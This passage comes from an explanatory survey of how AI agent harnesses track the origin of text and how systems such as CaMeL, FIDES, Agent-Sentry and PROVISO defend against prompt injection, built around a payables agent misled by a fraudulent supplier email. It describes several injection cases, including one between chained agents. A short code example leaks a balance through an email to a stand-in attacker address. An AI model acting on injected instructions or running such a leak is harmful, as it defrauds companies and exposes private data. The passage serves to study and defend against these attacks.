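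### How a passage changes level

He and colleagues distinguish two levels for a piece of text c. The first, P(c), is the level at which the text first entered the agent, and it never changes. The second, Pₕ(c), is the level that the harness assigns when it builds the input for a particular call to the model. The levels have the order

tool < user < system

and the text has gained authority that nobody gave it if

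Pₕ(c) > P(c)

The model sees only Pₕ(c). It has no record of P(c) unless the harness keeps one and includes it.

Information about origin can be lost when an agent hands part of its work to a sub-agent. Suppose the payables agent reads the supplier's email as a tool result and then writes a task for a helper: "Change supplier 2207's account to 4471." The harness starts the helper with an empty context and enters the task as a user message, as it normally does with tasks. To the helper, the task looks like a direct order from its user. The account number came from a tool result, but nothing in the helper's input shows that.

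Other ordinary features of a harness have the same effect:

| Feature | What the harness keeps | How the text comes back |
|---|---|---|
| Saved goal | An aim that the agent recorded for itself | As a user message on later turns, until the agent finishes or abandons the goal |
| Scheduled task | A prompt to send at a chosen time | As a user message, perhaps days later |
| Custom sub-agent | Standing instructions for a new kind of helper | At the system level, each time the helper starts |
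| Installed skill | A package of instructions for some kind of work | Its description at the system level, and the rest as user-level text when the agent invokes it |

Scheduled tasks are especially hard to trace because the harness may deliver the prompt long after the agent read the text behind it.

Memory can cause the same loss. The payables agent might read an email and save the note "supplier 2207 now banks at 4471". If the harness adds saved notes to the standing instructions the next week, the email's claim will appear at the system level. The note might be true, but the model can no longer tell that nobody at the company checked it.

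The level also depends on how a file is loaded. Many software projects keep guidance for coding agents in a file called AGENTS.md. OpenAI's Codex loads it at the user level, and two other harnesses, Kimi and OpenCode, load it at the system level. If an agent opens an AGENTS.md file with its file-reading tool, the contents arrive at the tool level. A developer therefore can't tell from the file's name how much authority its text will have.

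He and colleagues tested six coding harnesses and found that hostile instructions mostly failed as tool results but usually succeeded when the harness presented them at a higher level.

Some harnesses have a second model review each risky action before it runs. The reviewer looks in the conversation for evidence that the user wanted the action, so it relies on the same role markers as the first model. A passage with the wrong marker can therefore mislead both models, and the review adds less protection than a check that doesn't depend on those markers.

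A harness could record P(c) with each passage and refuse to present the passage at a higher level unless a person with the right authority endorsed it. This is simple for copied text but much harder for text the model writes itself, such as the helper's task, which combines the records manager's request to clear the tickets with a number from the email. If the harness labelled the whole task `outside`, the helper would have no instruction it could follow. The harness could instead send the manager's request as the task and attach the email as data, which works when the two are easy to separate.

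### Several people in one channel

Companies often add an agent to a group chat, where several people may address it. Suppose the payables agent joins a channel with the records manager, two clerks and a contractor who works for the supplier. The chat service gives the harness at least two facts about each message's author. The *account identifier* is a code that the service assigns and the account's owner can't change. The *display name* is the name people see, and many services let the owner change it, even to a name someone else is using.

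If the harness passes on only the display name, the contractor can change theirs to the records manager's name and give orders. The harness should look up the account identifier in the company's directory and pass on who the person is and what they may request. It should also send each person's message to the model as a separate item. If it pastes the whole conversation into one block, a clerk can fake a message from the manager by starting a new line with the manager's name.

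Even when people are named correctly, the interface is built for one person. Chen and colleagues note that developers train models to answer a single user based on the whole conversation, and that this training usually combines people's preferences into one overall score. This training doesn't represent several people with different aims and authority. In some of the settings they reviewed, assistants treated other people's speech as the main user's own input.

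The company still has to decide whose instructions the agent should follow. If everyone in the channel can use all of the agent's permissions, a clerk who can't edit bank details can get the agent to edit them. The agent is then a confused deputy, using its permissions on behalf of an employee who lacks them. The harness can prevent this by handling each request with the permissions of the person who made it, for example with an access token in that person's name.

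But the speaker's rights don't account for other people's influence on the request. The records manager might write "go ahead with the change we discussed" after the contractor has posted a different account number. The agent would then act on the contractor's number with the manager's permissions. The rule from Willison and Bista would reduce the agent's rights to those of the least trusted person whose words it had read. In a busy channel the agent could then do very little, so a separate approval of the exact account number is more practical.

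Anthropic's constitution lets an operator tell Claude which users have authority over which matters, just as a company divides responsibilities among its staff. This is useful for ordinary disagreements, such as when a clerk and the manager want tickets handled in a different order. But for bank accounts, it relies on the model to remember who has authority over what and apply that correctly every time.

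### Do models respond to the source?

Liao, Huang and colleagues (2026) tested whether a model's next action changes when only the stated source of a fact changes (*Auditing Provenance Sensitivity in LLM Agent Action Selection*). They prepared 450 tasks, each with one correct action. Each task's context mixed authorised evidence, such as the user's current request, with material that had no authority over the decision, such as an old preference or a stranger's note.

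They judged authority separately for each part of an action. In their example, a user asks an agent to send a contract to Alice, and an old note contains a different address. The note doesn't affect the decision to send an email, but it could lead the agent to use the wrong address. In the payables case, the supplier's email could properly lead the agent to open a change request, but it would have no authority to set the account number in the database.

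The main experiment added one statement to a context, once with a line marking its source as trusted and current, and once with a line marking its source as untrusted and external. The statement's wording and position stayed the same. Some statements supported the correct action, and others supported a competing one.

The researchers first measured how strongly four models favoured the correct answer, using log-odds, the logarithm of p/(1 − p) where p is a probability. A competing statement lowered the log-odds by 2.08 on average when it came from a trusted source and by 1.10 when it came from an untrusted one. For an answer one token long, this is like dividing the odds of the correct answer by 8 and by 3, respectively. The untrusted label considerably reduced the statement's effect, but the effect was still substantial.

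They then had five models choose complete actions. Changing the label changed the relevant part of the action in 5.4% of cases with competing statements and 1.7% of cases with supporting ones. Most of the changes were improvements. When the label on a competing statement went from trusted to untrusted, 4.0% of the answers went from wrong to right and 1.2% went from right to wrong. The error rates show what remained:

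| Model | No added statement | Competing, trusted source | Competing, untrusted source |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-4B | 3.6% | 3.9% | 3.0% |
| Mistral-Small-3.2-24B | 1.0% | 4.5% | 2.7% |
| Qwen3-30B | 2.0% | 6.3% | 6.0% |
| Llama-3.3-70B | 6.1% | 14.7% | 7.4% |
| DeepSeek-V2-Lite | 20.5% | 31.7% | 28.1% |
| All five | 6.7% | 12.2% | 9.5% |

Llama mostly discounted the untrusted statement. Qwen3-30B made almost as many errors with the untrusted statement as with the trusted one, so a company couldn't assume that a larger model from the same family is more sensitive to sources.

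These tests included a written policy about which sources could decide what. Without the policy, the error rate with untrusted competing statements rose to 14.9%. The policy helped Mistral most, cutting its errors from 20.8% to 2.7%, and had no measurable effect on DeepSeek. It also reduced errors when the competing source was trusted, but barely affected the share of actions that changed with the label. The policy seems to have made the models more careful in general without making them more sensitive to the source.

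An agent that acts correctly when it has valid evidence can also act on the wrong evidence when the valid evidence is missing. In one task, the user authorised two bags for a flight, but an old preference was for four. Qwen3-4B chose two. When the researchers removed the user's authorisation, it chose four, and when they removed the old preference as well, it returned to two. This pattern occurred in 2.4% of the comparisons in which they removed a piece of valid evidence. A payables agent could likewise pass every test while the supplier database was working, then take an account number from an email when the database failed to respond.

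Louck and colleagues found no benefit from rewording a dishonest description as a statement by its publisher. Their agents had to infer that a publisher has no authority to describe a rival, whereas Liao and colleagues explicitly labelled the source as untrusted.

The results come from tasks designed to be difficult, so they don't show how often deployed agents make these mistakes. The main tests used only open-weight models, most of them small by current standards. The prompt identified the source in a line of text, so the experiment doesn't show how models respond to real role markers or tool channels. Even people found it hard to decide what each source may determine. Three outside annotators relabelled part of the data, and their agreed labels matched the researchers' labels in 78.9% of cases.

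### Supplying origin outside the text

If a label in the text is only more text, the harness could give the model the origin of each token through a separate input. ASIDE does this for two classes, instructions and data. Zhang, Huang and Gu (2026), in *Origin Is All You Need*, use four classes, which they call rings, and build them into more of the model:

| Ring | Source | Treatment |
|---|---|---|
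| 0 | The operator's instructions | The model follows them. |
| 1 | The model's own earlier output | The model builds on it. |
| 2 | The user, and other content the application permits | The model treats it as part of the task. |
| 3 | Untrusted outside content | The model suppresses it. |

The application assigns a ring to every token according to how it arrived, without examining what it says. The ring then affects the calculation in two places. At the input, the model adds a learned list of numbers for the ring to the token's usual embedding:

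xᵢ = E(tᵢ) + α · O(rᵢ)

Here E(tᵢ) is the ordinary embedding of token i, O(rᵢ) is the embedding of its ring, and α is a learned number that controls the strength of the ring's signal. An attacker can choose the token but not the ring.

The second change is to *attention*, the step in which the model decides how much each token should draw on earlier ones. An ordinary model gives each pair of tokens a score based on their content. The new model adds a number that depends only on their rings:

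score(i, j) = (qᵢ · kⱼ)/√d + B(rᵢ, rⱼ)

The first term is the usual content score. B is a table of 16 learned numbers, all but two of which start at zero. Those two apply when a token from the user or from the model's own output attends to an untrusted token, and they start at −δ, where δ is large. The model turns scores into weights with an exponential function, so this multiplies the untrusted token's weight by e^(−δ) before the weights are scaled to add up to one. If δ were 10, an untrusted token would receive about 0.005% of the weight of a trusted token with the same content score. The user's tokens are restricted too because they could otherwise pass untrusted content on to the model's output.

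Zhang and colleagues added these parts to four existing models and trained them in two stages. The first used 105,000 examples of conversation, school subjects, mathematics and programming, so that the models could relearn ordinary work with the new parts in place. The second used 60,200 examples, of which 24,079 contained an injected instruction that the model had to ignore. For comparison, the researchers also trained the same models on examples of this kind without the new parts. These are the attack success rates for LLaMA-3-8B:

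| Test set | Original model | Training only | Training and rings |
|---|---|---|---|
| Held-out examples like the training data | 32.5% | 0.8% | 0.7% |
| Text classification | 21.3% | 2.3% | 0.03% |
| A smaller classification set | 24.1% | 8.6% | 0% |
| Mathematics problems | 17.2% | 0.3% | 0% |

Training alone accounted for nearly all of the protection against familiar attacks. The rings made more difference against unfamiliar ones, and their effect was larger for Mistral-7B. In the first classification set, 17.8% of attacks on that model succeeded after training alone and 0.03% succeeded with the rings. The defence also worked against attackers who knew the model's weights. One such attack succeeded in 50.7% of cases against the original LLaMA model and 1.4% against the protected one.

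Most of the protection comes from the attention table. When the researchers set it to zero in the finished LLaMA model, attacks on the first test set succeeded 72% of the time, more than twice the rate for the original model. The finished model evidently depended on the table and had not learned another way to resist injected instructions.

The measured loss of quality on ordinary requests was moderate. A judging model compared the protected and original models' answers to 805 requests, where a score of 50% means the two were equally good. The protected versions scored 60.9% for Qwen2.5-7B, 49.5% for the small SmolLM2-360M, 48.8% for LLaMA-3-8B and 42.7% for Mistral-7B. Skipping the first stage of training barely affected security but reduced LLaMA's score to 28.7%.

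These requests don't test cases where the model needs untrusted content to do its job. Zhang and colleagues acknowledge that the model suppresses everything in ring 3, including useful facts. If the payables agent's harness put the supplier's email there, the model could hardly read the new account number, but if it put the email in ring 2, the model would read both the number and any instruction hidden beside it. The researchers suggest adding more rings, or suppressing mixed sources less strongly and using a separate detector for suspicious passages.

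The training data also make the task easier than it would be in practice. The researchers placed an injected instruction inside a document, then labelled the injected words ring 3 and the rest of the document ring 2. A real harness can label an email as written by an outsider, but it can't identify which sentence in it is hostile. If it could, it could delete the sentence. The low attack rates are therefore good evidence that a model can be made to ignore tokens that the software has marked, but weaker evidence that an agent could read a stranger's email safely.

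The rings also depend on the harness to keep the labels correct as text moves. If the payables agent copied account 4471 into a task for a helper, and the harness entered that task as the user's request, the number would be in ring 2 and the attention table would not restrict it.

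## How can origin be tracked from the text an agent reads to the action it takes?

A model may act on text despite its origin label, but the harness can enforce the label. The harness labels each piece of text on arrival, works out a label for everything the agent derives from that text, and checks those labels before carrying out an action. Computer scientists call this *information flow control* and have studied it since the 1970s. GitHub's read and write rules apply it to whole issues and comments, but a harness can also apply it to single values, such as an account number.

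### How labels combine

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, use two basic integrity labels, trusted (T) and untrusted (U). When an agent derives something from two inputs, the result gets the *join* of their labels, written ⊔:

T ⊔ T = T

T ⊔ U = U

U ⊔ U = U

A result is therefore never more trusted than its least trusted input. Before a consequential action, such as a payment, the harness checks the labels on the decision to act and on each argument (a value passed to the tool). Under a strict policy, it blocks the action if any label is U.

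The same method works with more detailed labels. An integrity label can list everyone who could have written a value, and the join merges the lists. A secrecy label can list everyone allowed to read the value, and the join keeps only the people on both lists. If Ann, Bob and Carol may read one file and Bob, Carol and Dev may read another, the agent may send a summary of both only to Bob and Carol.

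Suppose the records manager asks the payables agent to clear today's supplier tickets, and one of them contains the email about account 4471:

| Item | Label | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| The manager's request | T | The manager logged in and sent it. |
| The ticket text | U | It contains an outsider's email. |
| Account number 4471 | U | The agent extracted it from the ticket. |
| Supplier number 2207 | U | It came from the company's database, but the name in the ticket determined which record the agent looked up. |
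| The call `update_account(2207, 4471)` | U | Both arguments are U. |

The harness refuses the change. If the manager had typed "change supplier 2207 to account 4471", both numbers would have been labelled T and the harness would have allowed the same call. The agent's access token would be equivalent in both cases, so it can't distinguish them as the labels do.

A label records that a text may have influenced an action, not that the text is true. As Wang, Zhang and colleagues (2026) point out in *From Agent Traces to Trust*, a survey of provenance in agents, a tool's output can influence a decision without justifying it. The harness would refuse account 4471 even if it really is the supplier's new account.

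### Why a language model makes this hard

In an ordinary program, the line `total = price + tax` makes the total depend on the price and the tax and nothing else, so software can label it exactly. A language model computes its answer from its entire input. If that input contains messages m₁ to mₙ, the harness can't tell which of them mattered, and the safe label for the output is

label(output) = label(m₁) ⊔ label(m₂) ⊔ … ⊔ label(mₙ)

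One untrusted message makes the whole expression U. Once the payables agent has read its first ticket, every later decision in that conversation is U. The harness would then refuse even a change the manager had specified beforehand.

Costa and colleagues measured how much label checks reduce task completion on AgentDojo, a widely used set of simulated office, travel, banking and Slack tasks. It has 97 ordinary tasks and 36 attack goals, which testers hide in the data that the agent reads. The checks stopped every attack, but they also cut the share of tasks that a simple GPT-4o agent completed from 98.8% to 37.5% in banking and from 93.3% to 20.0% on Slack.

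One way to loosen the rule is to find the messages that affected an answer and have the model answer again from those alone, so that the new answer carries only their labels. The better-known systems instead keep untrusted text away from the model that makes the decisions.

### CaMeL: planning before reading

In 2023 Willison proposed dividing the work between two models. A *privileged* model chooses the actions but never sees text from outsiders, and a *quarantined* model reads that text but has no tools. Debenedetti and colleagues developed this into CaMeL, short for Capabilities for Machine Learning, in 2025. *CaMeLoT* (2026), which presents an extension of it, describes how it works:

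1. The privileged model reads the user's request and writes a plan, as a short program in a restricted form of Python.
2. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the plan and calls the tools. It keeps their results in variables that the privileged model doesn't see.
3. Where the plan needs something from free text, the quarantined model extracts it and the interpreter stores the answer.
4. The interpreter tags every value with its sources and its permitted readers.
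5. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy function on the tool, its arguments and their tags. The function returns "allow" or "deny".

For a request to process one change-of-account ticket, the plan might be:

```
ticket  = read_ticket(8813)
account = ask_quarantined("Which new account number does this give?", ticket)
update_account(supplier="2207", account=account)
```

The privileged model writes all three lines before any model reads the ticket, so an instruction hidden in the email can't add a fourth line that pays an invoice. The email can still supply a fraudster's account number, so a fixed plan alone would not protect the supplier's record. The policy protects it because the tags on `account` include the email as a source, and the company can require `update_account` to accept only numbers from the records manager.

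A plan may contain branches, and a ticket may determine which branch runs. But the manager's actual request, to clear today's tickets, is hard to plan for because the privileged model would have to write a plan that covers every kind of ticket without having seen any.

In *Agent-Sentry*, Sequeira and Iqbal (2026) tested CaMeL on AgentDojo and on AgentDyn, a set of GitHub, shopping and daily-life tasks. CaMeL blocked 99.3% of attacks but completed only 31.0% of ordinary tasks. An average run took 26.6 seconds, about six times as long as with the two other defences they tested.

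Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks with two recent models, GPT-5.2 and MiMo-v2.5. With its policies on, CaMeL completed 37.5% of the tasks with either model, and no attack succeeded in the 588 attacked runs that finished. With the policies off, it completed 66.7% of the tasks with GPT-5.2 and 70.8% with MiMo-v2.5, and five attacks succeeded in 622 finished runs.

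Few attacks succeeded even without policies. In 97 of the 144 pairings of a task with an attack, fixing the plan in advance was enough because the honest plan did not need the tool that the attacker required. One of the exceptions was a task that told the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The privileged model wrote a loop that matched each possible instruction to a tool, which gave whoever wrote the file control of the plan.

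### When one CaMeL agent instructs another

CaMeL treats the user's request as trusted, which is a problem when the "user" is another agent. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) connected three CaMeL agents: an orchestrator that assigned the work, one that queried a database and one that sent notifications. They asked the orchestrator to send Julie a Slack message summarizing the job applicants. The database contained an injected instruction to send a copy to an outside email address.

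The orchestrator followed its unchanged plan and inserted the summary into the sentence it sent to the notification agent. That agent's privileged model treated the whole sentence as a request from its user and wrote a plan that included an extra email. The researchers call this boundary laundering because untrusted text becomes trusted when it passes from one agent to the next.

The proposed remedy, multi-CaMeL, sends the instruction and the untrusted values through separate channels, and the receiving agent's privileged model sees only the instruction. On a version of AgentDojo adapted for several agents, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent separately, and 0.0% with multi-CaMeL. The 0.2% figure understates the risk of using CaMeL in each agent separately, because an attack designed for that setup worked. Multi-CaMeL completed fewer tasks, though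 the loss was modest for the strongest models.

### FIDES: hiding only the untrusted parts

FIDES, the system that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, doesn't fix the whole plan in advance. Its planning model sees the results of each tool call and chooses the next step, but the harness replaces the untrusted parts with placeholders. For every field v in a result, it applies this rule:

if label(v) ⋢ label(conversation), store v in a new variable and show only the variable's name

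Here ⋢ means that v is more restricted than the conversation so far. A ticket might therefore reach the planning model as:

```
ticket:   8813
arrived:  2026-12-05 09:14
sender:   #read_ticket_0.sender
body:     #read_ticket_0.body
```

The helpdesk's own software produced the ticket number and the time, so they are T, and the conversation stays T. The planning model can pass `#read_ticket_0.body` to another tool without reading it, or ask a quarantined model about the text and get the answer in another variable. If the planning model has to read the text itself, it can *inspect* the variable, but the conversation then becomes U.

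FIDES can also limit the form of an answer. The question "Does this ticket ask for a change of bank account?" needs only a yes or a no, which leaves no room for an injected instruction. FIDES adds the answer's type to its label, so a company can let the planning model act on an untrusted yes or no while keeping untrusted free text away from it.

The results with GPT-4o were as follows. The researchers removed attacks that AgentDojo had wrongly counted as successful, and the last four columns give the percentage of tasks completed when there was no attack:

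| Agent | Successful attacks | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Simple agent, no checks | 152 | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| Simple agent with checks | 0 | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| FIDES with checks | 0 | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |

Hiding data in variables let the agent complete a good part of the tasks it had lost to the checks, except in travel. There, the checks had not reduced the number of tasks the simple agent completed, and GPT-4o had trouble using the variables. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks.

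The way the researchers labeled the data limits what the zero shows. AgentDojo has no integrity labels of its own, so they marked a field as untrusted if at least one attack in the test set used it. Their labels therefore could not miss an attack in the test. A company that labels the fields in its own helpdesk has no such list of attacks. The tests also left out the limits on the form of an answer, so they provide no evidence about those limits.

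### Agent-Sentry: checking where each argument came from

CaMeL and FIDES both require a company to rebuild its agent around variables. Sequeira and Iqbal's Agent-Sentry leaves the agent much as it is and examines each proposed action. The harness instructs the model to report, for every argument, which earlier message or tool result it came from and whether the model copied it, derived it or made it up. The reports form a graph of how values moved through the run. A proposed action then passes through up to three checks:

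1. A classifier computes 17 features of the graph, such as the share of arguments from untrusted sources, and estimates the probability that the action is an attack. It allows the action below 0.33 and blocks it from 0.66 upwards. Anything in between goes to the next check.
2. A lookup allows the action if its sensitive values have appeared in earlier legitimate runs and come from a trusted source this time.
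3. A language model compares what remains with the user's request and with short excerpts from the untrusted sources.

Tracking a value's origin can help catch attacks that a list of permitted values can't. In one of the test tasks, the user asks the agent to delete a calendar event, and an injected instruction tells it to email lily.white@gmail.com. Other users have good reasons to write to Lily, so a list must either include her address and let the attack through or exclude it and block legitimate tasks. Agent-Sentry detects that the address came from a tool result, and the language model finds nothing about sending an email in the user's request.

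In Sequeira and Iqbal's 5,380 recorded runs by seven simulated agents, Agent-Sentry allowed 96.4% of the honest runs and blocked 96.8% of the attacks, and it used the language model for only 3.1% of actions. On the original AgentDojo and AgentDyn tasks, they report 95.1% and 94.3%, but that version was tested on the same runs it learned its rules from. On runs not used for learning, a version with simple rules allowed 87.1% of honest runs and blocked 93.2% of attacks. The trained classifier allowed 69.1% of honest runs and blocked 91.2% of attacks, partly because it was trained on few honest examples.

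Agent-Sentry also relies on the model to report where values came from, and an injected instruction may distort that report. The software checks whether a value the model claims to have copied appears in the stated source, which reduces the problem but does not eliminate it.

The last check has a more serious weakness for the payables agent. The language model allows a value that appears in a source's normal content and blocks one that appears in a command or a claim of authority. Sequeira and Iqbal acknowledge that this won't reliably stop a realistic fake invoice with the attacker's account number in it. A politely worded email about account 4471 poses much the same problem.

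### PROVISO: learning when origin matters

Yan, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *PROVISO*, published in October, have a neural network learn the whole decision. In their example, the user wants an invoice paid to account B, but a line in the invoice redirects the payment to account C. The agent may take the amount from the invoice, but only the user can choose the recipient. The researchers don't program this rule into the system. The network learns from examples of actions and their outcomes, and it works in four steps:

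1. Software sorts the available text into four roles: trusted material such as the user's request (K), external material such as the invoice (G), the action that the agent proposes (P₀) and an alternative (P₁). The alternative can be a refusal or another way to continue.
2. A text encoder turns each segment into a list of numbers zⱼ, and the network adds a learned vector for the segment's role, so that mⱼ = Wzⱼ + b + e(rⱼ). The same sentence then has one representation when the user wrote it and another when it came from an invoice.
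3. The network searches these representations, compares what it finds and searches again. In the example, the first search can find that the proposed recipient isn't the user's, and the next can find where that recipient came from.
4. The network estimates how likely each action is to be both safe and useful, and the harness carries out the one with the higher score after an adjustment that sets how cautious the system should be.

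The alternative matters because blocking an action has a cost too. If the harness simply refuses to pay account C, the invoice stays unpaid.

With PROVISO, an agent running Google's Gemma 4 31B completed 87.6% of AgentDojo tasks without attacks and 85.4% under attack, and 0.28% of attacks succeeded. With SecAlign, which trains the model itself to resist injected instructions, the completion rates were 88.7% without attacks and 83.4% under attack, and 3.46% of attacks succeeded. On a separate test of individual tool calls, PROVISO missed one unsafe call and blocked five harmless ones.

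These figures are impressive, but the AgentDojo test is weak evidence about tracking origin. PROVISO chose between two complete attempts at the task, and the external text entered the network as part of those attempts rather than under its own role. The harness also had to try both attempts in a copy of the environment first, and a bank may not provide such a copy. PROVISO needs labelled examples from each new setting. Yan and colleagues did not test it against attacks designed to defeat it, or compare it with CaMeL or FIDES on these tasks.

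### What the LLMbda calculus proves

A learned check that performs well on every known attack can still fail on the next one. Garby and colleagues set out to prove a guarantee instead. They designed the LLMbda calculus, a small programming language for agents in which every value and every conversation with a model has a label. A program can copy a conversation, use the copy to read something untrusted, and then discard the copy. This lets programmers build the separation between two models themselves, without a fixed architecture.

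Their main theorem concerns *noninterference*. Suppose the payables agent runs twice with the same request from the manager but a different email in the ticket. Noninterference means that everything labelled T at the end is the same in both runs, so the email can affect only results labelled U. Because a model's answers vary at random, the theorem compares the probabilities of the trusted results. Call these μ with the first email and ν with the second. If the program always finishes, μ = ν.

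An agent may not finish, though, because a failed label check stops it, and the email can influence whether that happens. The theorem permits this but limits the effect:

½ Σ |μ(q) − ν(q)| ≤ (a + b)/2

The sum runs over all possible trusted results q, and a and b are the probabilities that the program fails to finish when given each email. If 2% of runs fail to finish with one email and 4% with the other, the left-hand side can be at most 0.03. A fraudster can therefore make the agent stop but can't steer its trusted results.

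The theorem covers every program in the language, including code that the model writes while the agent runs. Lean, a program that checks mathematical proofs, has verified the theorem. The same verified development includes the interpreter that calls the model.

Such care is worthwhile because label tracking is easy to get wrong. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL misses a leak that computer scientists have known about since the 1970s. In outline, it works like this:

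```
a = True
b = True
if balance > threshold: a = False
if a: b = False
if b: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the third line changes `a` and marks it as secret. The assignment in the fourth line then doesn't run, so CaMeL never marks `b` as secret and the email goes out, even though the value of `b` now reveals the balance. The same researchers also found that CaMeL loses track of an untrusted value when the plan inserts it into a longer piece of text. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) had already warned that Python's flexibility prevents strong guarantees about information flow, and recommended a language designed for security.

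### What the theorem assumes

The most important assumption is that labels are correct when data enters the program. If an employee pastes an email into a note and the helpdesk labels the email T, the agent can change the record to account 4471 without violating the theorem, because the email never had the label U.

Garby and colleagues also assume that the company has put a check on every sensitive tool, and that all data sources are inside the program. But real agents use outside systems. If an agent writes untrusted text to a shared folder and another program later returns it with the label T, the proof does not cover this case. Finally, they assume that each answer depends only on the conversation that the program sent. A model provider that carried memories between conversations would break that assumption.

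To test the language on real tasks, the researchers wrote an agent called Randori. It first practises its plan on made-up data, so that error messages from failed attempts can't bring in untrusted text, and then runs the finished plan for real. With three models, it completed between 64.6% and 75% of the AgentDojo banking tasks. Attacks succeeded in two of 1,296 attacked runs, both times by exploiting the one construct that the guarantee deliberately does not cover.

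### Endorsement

If an agent could never act on untrusted content, it couldn't buy the ingredients for a recipe or pay the amount on an invoice. Endorsement allows such actions by changing a label from untrusted (U) to trusted (T), and someone or something has to decide when the change is justified.

*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) describes Prudentia, an agent whose planning model can ask the user to endorse a hidden text before reading it. If an email lists ten jobs, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten separate actions. This saves time but has the same drawback as endorsing a whole helpdesk ticket, so approving each action individually is safer.

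Alternatively, a rule can decide. Garby and colleagues give the example of an agent that sorts an email into one of a few fixed categories and uses the category in its reply. With n categories, the sender can pass on at most log₂ n bits of information, or two bits for four categories. FIDES's limited answers use the same idea. This works well for sorting tickets, but the number of bits is a poor measure of harm. "Has the manager approved this change?" takes only one bit to answer, yet an agent that accepts a false answer from an email can lose the money.

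The hardest case is when a user delegates the decision to a document. One AgentDojo user asks the agent to read a text file and follow the payment instructions in it. Randori's model can endorse the file's contents when it writes the plan, before it has seen them. In the two successful attacks, both with GPT-5.2, the attacker had replaced the file with a different payment request. The agent paid the attacker even though every label was correct, because the user had asked it to follow the file's instructions.

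The researchers then removed endorsement from Randori and repeated the tests with the other two models. No attack succeeded, but the share of tasks completed fell from 75% to 62.5% with one model and from 64.6% to 54.2% with the other. The confidence intervals are wide because there are only 16 tasks, but some of the lost tasks can't be done without trusting a file.

Qu and colleagues' rule that delegated trust has a limited scope is hard to apply here, because "pay the bill in this file" sets no limits that software could check. A request that named the recipient and took only the amount from the file would give an attacker much less to manipulate.

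Garby and colleagues prove that a program can't leak its secrets by endorsing untrusted data, however much it endorses. They give no such guarantee about the endorsed data itself, and the language doesn't stop a planning model from endorsing too much.

People can also endorse the wrong thing because of what the agent tells them. Qu and colleagues rate CaMeL as fully protecting the agent's choice of actions and its data flows, but as offering no protection against biased judgement. The records manager might endorse account 4471 because the quarantined model's summary repeated the email's claim about a frozen account.

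### Security against usefulness

The results below come from different models and different attacks, so they give only a rough comparison:

| System | Tasks | Attacks that succeeded | Ordinary tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL with policies | AgentDojo banking | 0 of 588 | 37.5% |
| CaMeL | AgentDojo and AgentDyn | 0.7% | 31.0% |
| FIDES with checks | AgentDojo | 0 | 41.0% to 59.0% |
| Randori | AgentDojo banking | 2 of 1,296 | 64.6% to 75% |
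| Agent-Sentry with rules | AgentDojo and AgentDyn | 6.8% | 87.1% |
| PROVISO | AgentDojo | 0.28% | 87.6% |

Agent-Sentry's attack figure looks worse partly because its test contained only attacks that had already worked on an unprotected agent.

Critics of strict tracking have good evidence that it keeps agents from completing too many tasks. Sequeira and Iqbal cite a result in which CaMeL scored 0% on AgentDyn's open-ended tasks. According to Garby and colleagues, TypeGuard, another strict system, completed 15 of AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks with its policies off and 8 with them on. Its developers concluded that many of the tasks involve flows "that no secure policy would admit". Better models help an agent use variables, but they can't complete a task that the policy forbids. Someone also has to write a policy for every tool and keep it up to date.

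One argument for strictness is that probabilistic defences can fail when attackers adapt. Kolluri and colleagues cite experiments in which attackers defeated a combination of two training-based defences every time, and 12 other probabilistic defences with similar ease. A label check doesn't depend on how an attacker phrases an instruction. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) reports that attacks on one defence outside the model succeeded 4.2% of the time at first and 2.6% when the attacker adapted to it. The test was small and did not include CaMeL.

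Kolluri and colleagues also argue that the usual comparison is unfair. It compares a strict agent working alone with an unprotected one that, in practice, would ask a person for approval before every consequential action. They therefore counted the tasks each agent could finish without approval. With OpenAI's o3-mini, an agent that always asked finished 24.3% of AgentDojo's tasks, FIDES finished 50.1%, and Prudentia finished 59.1%. Prudentia does better than FIDES because its planning model is given the policies and can look for a plan that satisfies them.

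On WASP, a set of simple tasks on copies of GitLab and Reddit, Prudentia needed no approvals and no attack succeeded. With every model, it also completed at least as many tasks as the unprotected agent, because it never saw the injected instructions that distracted the other agent. These tasks suit it well, since posting a comment or upvoting doesn't require the agent to read what strangers have written.

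Kolluri and colleagues' argument is persuasive for agents that would otherwise need constant supervision. However, they assume that people answer correctly when the agent does ask, and they acknowledge that frequent requests lead people to approve without thinking.

A completion score can also count a sensible refusal as a failure. AgentDojo gives an agent credit for paying the bill described in a file, but many companies would want the agent to stop and check who wrote the file. The payables agent is right to refuse a bank account change requested in an email. The same strictness would be a nuisance for sorting tickets or drafting replies, where a mistake does little harm and a person will probably notice it. The company could enforce strict labels on payments and bank details and use a learned check such as Agent-Sentry for the rest, as long as a value that passes the learned check keeps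 its original label.

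## Can the source of an instruction be established after the agent has acted?

Suppose the company had none of these checks, and the payables agent changed supplier 2207's account to 4471. The company has since paid two invoices into that account, and the real supplier is asking for its money. An investigator has to trace the change in the database back to the words that caused it, and then to whoever wrote them. The company has a fraud to report if the words came from an outsider's email, but a problem with its own procedures if they came from a support employee's note.

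Three kinds of evidence could help establish the source. An *authorisation log* records which program used which credential and whether the service allowed the request. An *execution trace* records what the agent read and did, in order. *Causal attribution* is a finding, inferred from the other records, about which passage changed the agent's behaviour.

| Evidence | What it could reveal about account 4471 | What it would leave open |
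|---|---|---|
| Authorisation log | The payables agent made the change at 14:02 with a valid token in the records manager's name. | Why it did so |
| Execution trace | The agent had just read ticket 8813, where the number first appeared. | Whether the email or the employee's note in that ticket led to the change |
| Causal attribution | The request in the email led to the change, and the note made no difference. | Who wrote the email |

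### Why access logs stop at the agent

The IETF draft by Kasselman and colleagues sets a minimum for the authorisation log. For this change, an entry with the required information might be:

```
agent:     spiffe://example.com/finance/payables-agent
acted for: records.manager@example.com
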